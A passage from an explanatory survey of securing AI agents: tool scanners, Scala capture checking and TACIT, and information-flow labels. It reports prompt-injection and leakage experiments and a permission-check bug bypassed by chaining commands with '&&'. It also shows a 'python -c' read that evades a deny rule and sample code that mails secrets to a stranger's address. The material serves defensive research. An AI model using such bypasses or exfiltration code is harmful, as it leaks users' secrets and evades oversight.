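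Agent Audit found 40 of the 42 vulnerabilities in a benchmark that its developers built, and raised six false alarms. Two general-purpose scanners, Semgrep and Bandit, found 10 and 11 respectively, with no false alarms. The gap is partly because just over half of the benchmark's vulnerabilities involve MCP settings or exposed credentials, and Semgrep detected only one of those.

Agent Audit's taint analysis cannot offer a guarantee, for two reasons. It follows data only within a single function, so it can lose track of a model's reply when one function passes it to another. It also hides findings with a confidence score below 0.30. A finding inside a tool starts at 0.90, but Agent Audit multiplies the score by 0.20 if the code calls `isinstance()`, which checks a value's type. With no other adjustments, the score falls to 0.18 and the developer never sees the warning. This reduces false alarms,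 but confirming that a value is text does not make it safe to run as code.

An outside test gave much weaker results. In *AgentLens*, Lv, Chen and colleagues (2026) ran Agent Audit on two large open-source projects and manually checked its findings. It found three real vulnerabilities in the coding agent Aider and none in Langflow, a tool for building agents. Some of its false alarms were dummy keys in test files, which it reported as leaked credentials. AgentFuzz found three real vulnerabilities in Langflow and none in Aider. Lv and colleagues' own system, which combines code analysis with multi-step attacks on the running agent, found 11 in Langflow and 8 in Aider. The researchers have an interest in their own system doing well, but the comparison shows that both earlier tools missed real vulnerabilities.

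### More data than the task needs

Data can also leak through tools that have no coding flaw. *AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to email a payment's date and amount to an auditor. The agent reads the transaction record and also sends the card number and security code.

To find such leaks, their system first looks for pairs of tools where one could accept the other's type of output. A language model then removes pairs that make no sense together, such as reading an email and using the result to read an unrelated file. The remaining pairs form a graph of how data might move between tools. Compared with a graph the researchers had checked by hand, it contained 11 wrong connections and lacked 20 of 321 real ones. Because of the missing connections, the graph cannot rule out a leak, although Lin and colleagues describe it as an over-approximation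 of what the agent might do.

The graph mainly guides testing. The system writes prompts that should make the agent follow each chain of tools, runs them and records which data leaves. Three language models then vote on whether the task required each item. Of 608 chains, 347 (57%) exposed unnecessary data in at least one of five attempts. The researchers assembled the four test agents themselves and filled them with invented personal data, so this figure too is a poor guide to deployed products.

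Static analysis of the tools could not have settled the auditor case. The user wanted the agent to read a file and send an email, and the graph correctly permits both. Whether the email includes the card number depends on what the model writes. Information-flow labels instead attach restrictions to the data itself.

### Effects that a description leaves out

The scanners described so far mostly look for known kinds of mistake. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (2026), Adam, Lu and colleagues at Brown University pursue the more ambitious goal of listing everything a tool can do. Their example is a `write_file` tool that is described as writing text to a file, but also sends the text's length to a metrics service. A company working on confidential software might not want that, but neither the user nor the model can learn about it from the description.

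Adam and colleagues' analyser follows the tool's code down to the library functions that write files or open network connections. It then produces a "synopsis", a summary of the effects each input can influence. For `write_file`, the synopsis links the path to a file write, and the text to both a file write and a network write.

The network write reveals the hidden metrics traffic. If the user's policy forbids network access for sensitive code, the scaffolding can refuse the tool call before it starts. This is reliable only if the analyser accounts for every possible effect. If it cannot classify a low-level operation, it should reject the tool or assume the operation could have any effect.

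The same caution makes static analysis too strict for some policies. Suppose the user allows writes only inside the project folder. Because the model supplies the path at runtime, the analyser cannot determine where the tool will write and has to reject the tool, even if every write would have stayed inside the folder.

Adam and colleagues solve this with small sandboxes inside the tool. The developer replaces each direct file write with a version that checks the path against the user's policy at runtime. A second static analysis then confirms that every restricted effect goes through a sandbox and that no code alters the policy.

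The study compared four forms of protection in three scenarios: writing configuration files, editing confidential code with the `write_file` tool, and publishing a project that might contain a secret key. Each scenario had one version the user would want and one the user would not.

| Protection | Wanted versions allowed | Unwanted versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One sandbox around all tools | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
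| Static analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Static analysis with small sandboxes | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

This is an early demonstration that used scenarios the researchers chose and policies they assumed were correct. The results still match the reasoning above. Static analysis alone blocked every unwanted action, but it also blocked legitimate file writes because it could not predict their paths.

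Closed and remote tools are harder to analyse because users cannot see their code. Adam and colleagues propose that the developer run the analysis and send the synopsis when the user's software connects. The user then needs evidence that the server is running the code the developer analysed. Remote attestation can provide this by using special hardware to confirm which program is on the server, but this adds the hardware to the trusted base.

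The analysis also stops where a tool hands work to another system, such as a shell command, a database or a web service. The prototype can limit which web domains a tool contacts, but it cannot distinguish a request that reads a social media post from one that publishes a post. The prototype works only on tools written in Rust, whose strict type system makes effects easier to trace. Many agent tools are written in Python or JavaScript, where Adam and colleagues expect a sound analysis to be much harder and to reject more harmless tools.

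## How does a capability-safe language limit what agent-written code can do?

Adam and colleagues' analyser has to search for a tool's hidden effects because most languages let any line of code cause them. A Python function called `count_words` can also open Michelle's mailbox or contact a web server, since file and network functions are available everywhere in the program. Security researchers call this ambient authority. In a capability-safe language, code can cause an effect only through a value it holds.

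### No reference, no effect

Coding agents often control ambient authority with rules about the text of commands, and *Language-Based Agent Control* gives two examples of how such rules fail. In March 2026, a bug made Claude Code check only the first of several commands joined with `&&`, so a forbidden command could follow a permitted one. A rule against reading `denied.txt` also misses `python -c "open('denied.txt').read()"`, because the rule applies to shell commands and does not cover the Python code inside them.

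In the object-capability model, the right to do something and the means of doing it are the same value. A file handle both identifies a file and lets its holder read it. The text `/home/michelle/inbox` names a folder but gives no access to it. Suppose Michelle's assistant passes her messages to a function called `summarise` and her outbox only to a function called `deliver`. Even if an attacker wrote every line of `summarise`, it could not send mail, because it has no access to the outbox or to anything else that can send mail.

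Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966 as unforgeable tokens that control access to a computer's resources. Operating systems such as Hydra and Fuchsia later adopted the idea. Mark Miller and colleagues brought it to programming in the language E, and Joe-E, a security-oriented subset of Java, also uses it. In both languages the token is an ordinary object reference.

The model works only if programs cannot forge references, for example by turning a number into a pointer. The language must also grant no authority by default, so it can have no global function that opens any file by name. The host system gives all its capabilities to the program's entry point, which passes them on to the functions that need them. This makes it easier to see which functions can do what, but passing capabilities through every call is tedious.

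*AgentCap* (2026) applies capabilities to agents at runtime. It treats every action a model proposes as an untrusted request that needs a capability to proceed. Suspicious requests lower the agent's trust level, and AgentCap can then revoke the agent's capabilities. A runtime check like this controls what an agent does, but it cannot show before code runs that the code will only compute.

### What a function may already hold

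Suppose the assistant needs a function that shortens a confidential message, and the model writes this one:

```scala
val shorten = (text: String) =>
  outbox.send("stranger@example.com", text)
  text.take(200)
```

`shorten` takes text and returns text, and the caller gives it no capability. But `outbox` was in scope where the model defined `shorten`, so the function kept a reference to it. A function that keeps references this way is called a closure. In most languages its type is "text to text", the same as for a harmless function that only cuts the message to 200 characters.

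If capabilities are untracked, an automatic check therefore cannot show that a computation is free of effects. A reviewer could read the function's code, but the check is meant to avoid relying on that. Odersky and colleagues see two solutions for a language like E or Joe-E. It could forbid closures from keeping any capabilities, which would make closures far less useful, or it could record in each value's type which capabilities the value holds.

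### Capabilities in the type

Scala 3 does the second of these with an extension called capture checking. The type `T^{x}` describes a value of type `T` that may hold the capability `x`, and the part in braces is its capture set. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives the example of a logger that writes to a file:

```scala
val out: File^ = new File("~/some/bits")
val lg: Logger^{out} = new Logger(out)
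```

The type of `lg` records that `lg` can reach `out`. The logger counts as a capability because any code that holds it can write to the file through it. A type with an empty capture set is pure, meaning its values hold no capabilities.

Functions have capture sets too, and Scala uses different arrows to distinguish them:

| Function type | Capabilities the function may hold |
|---|---|
| `String -> String` | None |
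| `String ->{f} String` | Only `f` |
| `String => String` | Any |

The compiler infers the capture set from the function's body. `shorten` uses `outbox`, so its type is `String ->{outbox} String`. The type would be the same if the call to `send` were inside a branch that never ran. The set can include capabilities that the function never uses, but the check is sound because the set must include every capability the function might use.

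A value with fewer capabilities can stand in for one with more. In symbols, where `<:` means "can be used as" and *C* and *D* are capture sets:

> If *C* ⊆ *D*, then `T^C <: T^D`.

A pure function can therefore be used wherever any function is allowed, but `shorten` cannot be used where the program requires a pure one. The compiler also tracks indirect access. Since `lg` can reach nothing but `out`, a value that captures `lg` can be used wherever one that captures `out` is allowed.

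Capture sets also let the compiler check each function using only its own code and the declared types of whatever it uses. The compiler therefore avoids the hardest part of the call-graph problem from the previous section, which is working out which functions each variable in the program could hold. Odersky and colleagues note that precise versions of this analysis take exponential time in the worst case.

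Mutable variables also count as capabilities. Otherwise a supposedly pure function could copy a secret into a shared variable for other code to read later. Tracking capabilities also makes them less tedious to use. Scala can pass them to functions implicitly, and it can allow global ones such as a console, because any function that uses the console has it in its capture set. Capture checking is still experimental, though according to Scala's documentation it is quite mature and should become stable soon.

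### Two programs the compiler rejects

The first program tries to keep access to a folder after its permission has ended. In a simplified form, the function that grants access has this signature:

```scala
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)
  (block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

It creates a capability for the folder `root`, passes it to a block of code, and returns the block's result, which has some type `T`. The capability should become invalid when the block ends. Odersky and colleagues show how a program might try to smuggle it out:

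```scala
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
bad()
```

The block does not read the file. It returns a function that will read the file when someone calls it, and the last line calls it after the block has ended. The compiler catches this as follows:

1. The returned function uses `fs`, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`.
2. That type would have to be `T`, the result type of `requestFileSystem`.
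3. `T` has to make sense outside the block, where `fs` does not exist, so it cannot mention `fs`.
4. No suitable `T` exists, and the compiler rejects the program before it opens anything.

An agent in their experiments made a more ordinary version of this mistake when it tried to return a list of file handles from such a block. It could have read the files inside the block and returned their text, because a string holds no capability.

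The second program leaks a secret. TACIT, the system that Odersky and colleagues built around capture checking, wraps confidential data in a container called `Classified`. Agent code cannot take the data out, but it can transform the data inside the container with a method called `map`:

```scala
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The thin arrow means that `op` must be pure. During the experiments, an agent with access to the project folder tried to write confidential text to a file from inside `map`. Shortened and with simpler names, its code did this:

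```scala
val notes = access("secrets/notes.txt")
report.map { text => notes.write(text) }
```

The function inside `map` uses `notes`, so its type is `String ->{notes} Unit`, where `Unit` means it returns nothing useful. The method requires `String -> Unit`, so the compiler rejects the snippet and reports that the file handle "cannot flow into capture set {}".

The destination was in the secrets folder, so the agent may have been trying to save confidential text in a suitable place. The check rejects every write inside `map`, whatever the destination. For legitimate writes, the library provides `writeClassified`, which accepts the container without opening it and writes only to protected files.

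### From a type system to an agent

TACIT, short for Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types, appeared in March 2026. It is an MCP server, so any agent that supports the protocol can use it without modification. The agent sends a Scala snippet as the argument of a tool call. The server compiles it and either runs it or returns the compiler's errors. Its guarantees depend on three properties of the language:

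- **Capability safety.** Code cannot forge a capability or drop one from a type while still holding it.
- **Capability completeness.** Every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, apart from effects that the runtime can contain. If one library function could reach the network without a capability, a "pure" function could call it and leak a secret.
- **Local purity.** A type can require that one piece of code hold no capabilities, while the rest of the program uses files and networks as usual.

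Full Scala lacks the first property because a programmer could use a type cast to relabel `shorten` as `String -> String` even though it still holds `outbox`. TACIT therefore compiles agent code in safe mode, a restricted form of the language that Scala's *Safe Mode* describes. Safe mode forbids unchecked casts and pattern matches, the unsafe parts of the capability library, annotations that turn checks off, and reflection, which finds and calls code by name at runtime. It also turns on capture checking, including for changes to mutable data, and allows access only to safe global objects.

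Some useful libraries cannot meet these rules. A cache, for instance, stores earlier results in a variable that the compiler does not track. A programmer who has verified such a module can mark it `@assumeSafe`, and agent code may then call it. The Scala documentation also uses this annotation for a mail function that shows each message to the user and sends it only after the user confirms. The consultancy VirtusLab notes that agent code cannot use the annotation, since a model could otherwise declare its own code safe.

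Safe mode does not track exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program. A pure function can still fail, and its error message might contain the secret it was processing. Tracking every possible failure would be impractical because almost any code can run out of memory or divide by zero. TACIT catches exceptions at runtime and turns them into ordinary values, which it can keep classified.

Code gets access to files, commands and the network through calls like `requestFileSystem`. A snippet requests a folder, a list of commands or a list of web hosts, and can use them only inside the block that follows. The compiler prevents the capability from escaping the block, and the library checks at runtime that each path lies inside the requested folder. Making a request also requires a capability, so a function inside `map` cannot gain new access to the disk or the network.

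The agent's code names the folder, commands or hosts it requests, and the types don't limit what it can name. An operator who wants to keep an agent out of `/home/michelle/private` has to build that limit into the library. Zhao and colleagues make a similar point about LACUNA, which fills gaps in a Scala program with generated code. The compiler enforces the limits of the capabilities a developer grants, but it doesn't determine which capabilities a task needs.

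### Working on text the agent cannot read

TACIT uses two output channels so that the user can see classified results that the agent cannot. When a snippet prints an ordinary value, the agent and the user see the same text. When it prints a classified value, the user sees the content on their own terminal, and the agent receives only `Classified(****)`.

The agent usually runs on a large cloud model. If a contract's text enters that model's conversation, the provider receives it, and the model may repeat it in a later tool call. TACIT instead lets snippets send classified text to a separate model that the operator trusts, usually a local one, and that model's answer is also classified.

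Suppose a user wants a summary of a confidential contract. The cloud model writes code that reads the file into a `Classified` container, passes the container to the trusted model and prints the answer. The user sees the summary, but the cloud model receives only confirmation that the code ran. If the user then asks for the summary's length, the cloud model can write `summary.map(_.length)`. The user sees the number, but the cloud model receives only asterisks. The container persists between turns, although the permission to read files ended with the code block that used it.

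Any hostile instructions in the contract could still influence the trusted model's summary, but they cannot make that model send anything because it has no tools. TACIT's operator also has to make sure that the trusted model does not retain text between requests, because the type system cannot check that.

In TACIT's original design, a programmer fixes the processing steps before seeing the document. In LACUNA, Zhao and colleagues let a trusted local model write new code inside `map` after reading the text, so the processing can adapt to the document. The compiler checks this code under the same purity rule, so it still cannot send the contents anywhere.

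The design assumes that the person at the terminal is authorized to read the data. If an intruder sits down at Michelle's computer and has the agent print a classified file, the user's channel will show the file's contents.

### Leaks with and without the types

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, making 120 trials. In another 11 trials, a malicious user asked for the secrets, five times directly and six times under a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency password change. They ran all 131 trials with each of two models, once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once as plain text. A trial counted as a leak if a secret appeared in the agent's output.

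| Model | Source of attack | Trials | Leaks with `Classified` | Leaks with plain text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Injection | 120 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | User's request | 11 | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Injection | 120 | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | User's request | 11 | 0 | 8 |

No trial leaked with types, while 1.5% of Claude's trials and 8.4% of MiniMax's leaked without them. The 11 malicious requests accounted for 10 of the 13 leaks.

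The injection results are weaker evidence for the type system than they look, because Claude resisted all 120 injections even when the secrets were plain text. The compiler may therefore have had little to block with the types enabled. The programs the compiler rejected are more informative. In one, an agent tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`, which the compiler blocked because printing requires a capability.

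*Language-Based Agent Control* reports a stricter test that assumes the injection has already worked. The test used ELBA, the paper's Haskell system, in which separate sub-agents read all outside data. Whenever a sub-agent read a poisoned message, the researchers replaced its entire prompt with the attacker's text, so the sub-agent pursued the attacker's goal. Across four models, ELBA resisted all 735 attacks per model with its policies on, while up to 42% succeeded with them off. The policies also cut completed tasks from 494–558 to 294–351. This protection came from labels that a library checks at runtime, so the result supports the broader approach more than capture checking in particular.

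In TACIT's leakage test, protecting the data did not reduce the amount of useful work the agents did. Claude answered correctly in 99.2% of the injection trials with classified data and 83.3% with plain text. MiniMax did so in 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Claude's low score with plain text is partly an artefact of their set-up, because Claude often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

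### Ordinary work in checked Scala

LACUNA solved 14 percentage points fewer tasks than an ordinary agent on τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark from the section on typed interfaces. TACIT did better on the two τ²-bench domains that Odersky and colleagues tried. The table gives the percentage of tasks solved, averaged over ten runs.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
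|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

TACIT led by 0.8 to 3.7 points in every comparison. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the compiler's error messages and the structured data types that TACIT's functions return. Writing a program instead of single calls may also have helped, but the experiment had no agent that wrote unchecked code, so it cannot separate these causes. The benchmark makes little use of capabilities, because the functions for booking flights or returning goods take and return plain data. The test therefore mainly shows that these models can write typed Scala.

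Comparing TACIT with LACUNA suggests that type checking alone did not cause LACUNA's loss. TACIT runs the conversation in an ordinary agent loop and type-checks only the code snippets, whereas LACUNA runs the conversation as a sequence of generated programs. The comparison is rough because the two studies used different models.

TACIT's compiler caused few retries and little delay. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets needed a retry, depending on the model and domain, and those that did needed fewer than 1.4 retries on average. Many of the errors were unrelated to security. For example, models often wrote `$50` inside a string, where Scala treats the dollar sign as the start of a variable. Checking a typical snippet took less than a second, far less than waiting for the model.

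On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved slightly fewer issues with TACIT (41.7%) than with its usual tools (43.3%), a difference of five. Odersky and colleagues think this is because programming tasks rely on shell commands, which fit less naturally into their library.

Developers also have to write the library and keep it correct. The reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and someone who understands capture checking has to write it. Each new set of tools needs a few hundred lines of type and function declarations, about as many as the JSON schemas they replace. A model can draft these declarations for a person to review.

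### TACIT beside CaMeL

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on the AgentDojo injection benchmark and compared its results with published scores for CaMeL. CaMeL, another defence against prompt injection, tracks data at runtime in its own interpreter for a subset of Python. Zhao and colleagues later added LACUNA to the comparison. The table gives the percentage of attack trials in which the agent still completed the user's task.

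| Domain | Trials | Gemini 2.5 Pro: CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA | o4-mini-high: CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 144 | 52.8 | 56.9 | 63.2 | 62.5 | 59.0 | 66.0 |
| Workspace | 560 | 53.8 | 50.5 | 56.3 | 81.4 | 52.9 | 55.5 |
| Slack | 105 | 48.6 | 40.0 | 42.9 | 68.6 | 47.6 | 49.5 |
| Travel | 140 | 1.4 | 64.3 | 63.6 | 74.3 | 68.6 | 71.4 |

TACIT and CaMeL were almost equally secure, with one attack succeeding against each across both models. In the attack on TACIT, the user asked the agent to book a hotel whose reviews contained an advertisement for another hotel. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews, and AgentDojo counts any mention of the other hotel as a successful attack. LACUNA also had few failures, with eight.

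With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 527 of 949 trials over all four domains and CaMeL completed 722, so "comparable", as Odersky and colleagues describe TACIT's task completion, is a poor description of these results. On workspace tasks, which involve email, calendars and files, TACIT completed 52.9% and CaMeL 81.4%, a gap of 160 trials. With Gemini, TACIT led by 497 to 430, but only because CaMeL completed just two travel trials. Without travel, CaMeL led narrowly, by 428 to 407.

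The paper does not explain the workspace gap. One possible cause is that the agent gets little feedback when its code goes wrong. In this version of TACIT, email and file contents come back classified, and if a function inside `map` throws an exception, TACIT hides the error in case it reveals classified content. The code seems to the agent to have worked, but the user sees an empty answer. TACIT's instructions warn the model about this at length, which suggests it was a real problem. LACUNA scored only a little higher than TACIT on the workspace tasks.

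The AgentDojo experiment also provides less evidence about local purity than the leakage test. There, `sendEmail` takes plain text and requires no capability, so the compiler does not reject a function inside `map` that sends mail. The instructions tell the model that side effects inside `map` happen immediately and that it should put them where it wants them. TACIT's resistance to these attacks therefore probably comes more from keeping tool results away from the agent's main model than from local purity. A separate model with no tools reads the results.

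### Haskell and effect types

Scala functions may have effects unless their types rule them out. Haskell makes purity the default, so a function's type must mention any effect it has. In ELBA, if a calculator program requires an agent's code to have the type `Int`, the code can compute a whole number but cannot delete a file while doing so. A few Haskell functions bypass this rule, but a restricted version of the language called Safe Haskell excludes them.

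Developers can also define narrower effects. *Language-Based Agent Control* describes an agent that compiles bibliographies whose entries must all come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. Its code can search DBLP, fetch an entry and append an entry to a file. The append function accepts only a `Trusted` entry, and only the fetch function can create one. The agent can sort and filter entries with any pure code, but it cannot write one from memory. Over 100 tasks, an ordinary agent with web search got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, while ELBA made no such errors in 925 citations.

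Odersky and colleagues object that Haskell lacks built-in object capabilities, so developers would have to encode them in complicated types. ELBA uses a simpler method for files. A `Path` is an unforgeable value that represents one folder and its contents, and the read function accepts a `Path` but not a string such as `"/etc/passwd"`. When code narrows a path, the library checks at runtime that the new path stays inside the original folder. This controls access, but the type of a file operation does not show which folder it uses, as a capture set would.

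*ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a language for agents. Each function's type lists the operations it may request, such as reading a repository or applying a patch. Developers can also set rules about the order of operations, for instance that a request for approval must come before any change to the repository. The compiler proves that the code follows these rules where it can, and a runtime monitor checks the rest.

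In a dry run, a developer replaces a real operation with a harmless imitation. Most languages that track effects would then remove the operation from the type. ETAS instead keeps a record of the request, so a reviewer agent that is supposed to be read-only cannot attempt a write even in a dry run. Tan and colleagues report that the checks gave the expected result in all their test programs and coding scenarios. However, the ordering rule covers only the first change to the repository, so a program could make several changes after one approval and still satisfy the rule.

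Other languages track authority in related ways. Wyvern, a research language, has a module system based on capabilities. Gradient tracks object capabilities in types to limit the damage a compromised library can do. Code from an untrusted model poses much the same problem as code from an untrusted library, although neither project was designed for agents.

### Capabilities at runtime

JavaScript and WebAssembly can limit authority without a new type system. Hardened JavaScript freezes the language's shared built-in objects and runs untrusted code in compartments, which start with no access to files or the network. The code can use only what the host passes in. As in E, a function's type doesn't show which capabilities the function holds.

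WebAssembly is a portable format for compiled programs, and its modules have no input or output by default. The host decides at launch which folders or network functions to provide, and VirtusLab notes that a function the host leaves out does not exist for the module. This approach works for code written in many languages, including Rust.

A sandbox normally applies its limits to a whole module. As Odersky and colleagues point out, a sandbox that lets an agent read a private file and call its cloud model cannot stop it from sending the file's contents to the model. A developer could put the step that handles private text in a separate module with no outside access, which would give something close to local purity. But someone would have to do this for each such step and pass data in and out of it, whereas Scala can require a single function in the middle of a program to be pure. The two approaches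 can also be combined, since Scala code can compile to WebAssembly.

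## How do information-flow labels keep secrets and untrusted data away from the wrong tool?

Michelle's assistant needs access to both her inbox and her outbox, so its program can copy a private message from one to the other. Capabilities limit which tools the program can use, but not what it writes in an email it is allowed to send. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) describes the same gap in ordinary access control, which decides who may open a file but not what happens to the contents afterwards. Information-flow control fills this gap by labelling each piece of data with how secret it is (its confidentiality) and how far it can be trusted (its integrity). The label follows the data through every copy and calculation. TACIT's `Classified` container is a simple case that labels data only for secrecy.

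### Which way data may flow

Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, gave labels their mathematical form. A policy has a finite set of classes and a rule for which class may flow into which. The simplest policy has two classes, public and secret, and forbids only flows from secret to public. When a program combines two values, the result takes the lowest class that both may flow into, called their join. The join of public and secret is secret, so a summary of a press release and a private email is secret.

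An ordering is a lattice if any two classes have a join and a highest class that may flow into both. Denning derived this structure from how programs move data. For example, if a program may copy `a` to `b` and then `b` to `c`, the policy must also allow a direct copy from `a` to `c`, because the program could get around a ban on the direct copy by copying in two steps.

The classes can also be sets of people allowed to read the data. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) does this in FIDES, a system from Microsoft. If Alice, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, then only Bob and Carol may read a text based on both.

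In 1973, David Bell and Leonard LaPadula set out rules for confidentiality. A process may not read data above its clearance or write to a place below it. Kenneth Biba later reversed these rules to protect integrity, so untrusted data must not flow into places that require trusted data. For example, a stranger's email may supply the text of Michelle's summary but not the recipient's address.

Sabelfeld and Myers point out that a program can corrupt trusted data without any outside influence, by calculating incorrectly. A "trusted" integrity label therefore means only that no untrusted source affected the value, which may still be wrong.

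### Copies and branches

The simplest leak is an explicit flow, in which a program copies a secret into a public variable with a line such as `leak = secret`. Implicit flows pass through the program's decisions instead. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives this example:

```text
if secret is even
  then leak = 0
  else leak = 1
```

Both assignments write a constant, yet `leak` ends up holding the last binary digit of `secret`. A program that did this for every digit would copy the whole number.

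To catch such leaks, a checker keeps a program-counter label, which records what data determined whether the current line runs. When the checker enters a branch, it joins the condition's label to the program-counter label and treats everything the branch writes as carrying the combined label. After the branch, it restores the earlier label, because the lines that follow run whichever branch was taken. In the example, the program-counter label is secret inside both branches, so neither may write to a public variable.

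Such a checker is meant to enforce noninterference, which requires that any two runs of a program with the same public inputs produce the same public outputs, even if their secret inputs differ. The integrity version requires that changing the untrusted inputs never changes a trusted output. Because both definitions compare runs, watching a single run cannot show that a program satisfies them.

Denning shows how this defeats a system that only updates labels at runtime, using a program by J. S. Fenton. Here `a` is secret, and `b` and `c` start out public:

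```text
b = false
c = false
if not a then c = true
if not c then b = true
```

If `a` is true, the program skips the first conditional assignment. `c` stays false and public, so the second test depends only on public data, and `b` becomes true and remains public. If `a` is false, `c` becomes true and secret, so the second test fails and `b` stays false and public. In both cases `b` ends up equal to `a` with a public label. The runtime system doesn't update a variable's label when it skips an assignment to that variable, even though skipping it also reveals something about `a`.

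One remedy at runtime is never to lower the program-counter label after the program branches on secret data. Sabelfeld and Myers explain that this works badly in practice because labels only become more restrictive as the program runs, a problem called label creep, and soon the program can send hardly anything. A static checker can avoid this because it analyzes the branches that do not run as well as the one that does.

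### Two typing rules

Volpano, Smith and Irvine (1996), in *A Sound Type System for Secure Flow Analysis*, turned Denning's analysis into a type system and proved it sound. These are their rules for assignments and conditionals, with the variables renamed:

```text
γ ⊢ x : τ var      γ ⊢ e : τ
------------------------------
γ ⊢ x := e : τ cmd

γ ⊢ e : τ      γ ⊢ c : τ cmd      γ ⊢ d : τ cmd
-------------------------------------------------
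γ ⊢ if e then c else d : τ cmd
```

The statement below a line holds if everything above the line holds. The symbol γ stands for the declared types of the variables, and τ is a security class, either *L* for public or *H* for secret. A variable of type `τ var` stores data of class τ or lower. A command of type `τ cmd` writes only to variables of class τ or higher.

The assignment rule requires the variable and the expression to have the same class. The checker may raise an expression's class from *L* (public) to *H* (secret) but may not lower it, so a program can copy public data into a secret variable but can't copy secret data into a public one.

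The conditional rule requires both branches to match the class of the condition. Here the checker can also treat an `H cmd` as an `L cmd`, because a command that writes only to secret variables meets the weaker requirement of writing to variables that are public or higher.

If `x` is public and `y` is secret in `if x = 1 then y := 1 else y := 0`, the checker can make the rule apply by either raising the condition to *H* or lowering the branches to *L*. If `x` is secret and `y` is public, the condition is *H* and the branches are `L cmd`. The checker can't lower the condition or raise the branches, so it rejects the program.

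The rules also prevent the leak in Fenton's program, because each variable has one fixed class. If `c` is public, the checker rejects the first conditional, and if `c` is secret, the second conditional requires `b` to be secret as well. The checker also rejects some safe programs. With a secret `x` and a public `y`, it rejects `if x = 1 then y := 0 else y := 0`, although both branches set `y` to 0 and so reveal nothing about `x`.

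Volpano and colleagues prove that in any program that passes the type check, changing the secret inputs does not change the final value of a public variable, provided the program finishes successfully. An attacker may therefore still learn something from whether a program stops. Sabelfeld and Myers list other channels that such a proof also doesn't cover, including running time and power use. Snelting and Wasserrab (2008), in *A Correctness Proof for the Volpano/Smith Security Typing System*, later produced a machine-checked proof for a simple language without threads.

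The languages Jif and Flow Caml implement these ideas. Jif adds labels to Java's types, and Flow Caml adds them to a language in the ML family, where the compiler can infer most of the labels.

### A plan in six kinds of step

Information flow is easier to check in a language small enough that every flow is visible to the checker. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) presents such a language for agents that keep information between requests. For each request, a model writes one complete plan before any tool runs. A checker then determines the label of every value in the plan, and an interpreter executes the plan exactly as approved.

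A plan can contain only six kinds of step:

| Step | What it does | How the checker treats it |
|---|---|---|
| `retrieve` | Loads a value saved during an earlier request | Restores the value's saved label |
| `tool` | Calls a tool | Tests the inputs, then labels the result |
| `q-llm` | Gives text to an isolated model that has no tools | Gives the output the combined label of the inputs |
| `display` | Shows something to the user | Blanks out any item the user may not see |
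| `condition` | Runs one of two lists of steps | Checks both lists under the condition's label |
| `loop` | Repeats steps for each item in a collection | Checks the steps under the collection's label |

The inputs to a step can only be constants, earlier results, fields of those results, or lists and records built from them. Plans can't do arithmetic or define functions. A condition can make only one simple comparison, such as whether one number is greater than another. These limits let the checker read every dependency directly from the plan. Any other work, such as finding an account number in a letter, goes to a tool or the isolated model.

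Each value has a confidentiality class *c* and an integrity class *i*. When a result depends on two values, SPA combines their labels like this:

> (*c*₁, *i*₁) ⊔ (*c*₂, *i*₂) = (*c*₁ ⊔ *c*₂, *i*₁ ⊓ *i*₂)

When two values are combined, the result takes the higher confidentiality and the lower integrity of the two. With two levels of each, the result is secret if either value is secret, and trusted only if both values are trusted. FIDES puts untrusted at the top of its integrity ordering and SPA puts it at the bottom, so their formulas look different, but in both, combining trusted and untrusted data gives an untrusted result.

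For a tool call, the checker first combines the labels of all the inputs with the program-counter label. Call the result (*c*, *i*). Whoever deploys the agent has given each tool a highest confidentiality it may receive, *C*, and a lowest integrity it will accept, *I*. The call passes if both of these hold:

> *c* ⊑ *C* and *I* ⊑ *i*

The symbol ⊑ means "at or below". If the call passes, its result gets the label (*c*, *i*) combined with a fixed label for that tool. The fixed label is needed because a harmless request can return sensitive or untrusted data. For instance, a search for "Acme" might return a letter from a stranger.

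If any step fails, SPA rejects the whole plan. It doesn't tell the planning model why or ask for another attempt, because Girrens and Wang want to prevent a model from revising an unsafe plan until it passes. TACIT and LACUNA, by contrast, return compiler errors to the model. If the check is sound and the policy is correct, retrying can't get a forbidden plan accepted. SPA's stricter rule is more useful if the policy has gaps that a model might find by retrying.

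### The attacker's account number

Girrens and Wang illustrate the danger with an invoice from a company called Acme. It contains an attacker's account number and a hidden instruction to the agent. The agent fetches the invoice on Monday, and on Tuesday the user asks it to pay. The check is easiest to follow if Michelle first asks for both at once. In a shortened notation, the plan might be:

```text
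1. invoice = tool find_invoice(vendor: "Acme")
2. details = q-llm(invoice, "extract the account and amount")
3. receipt = tool pay(account: details.account,
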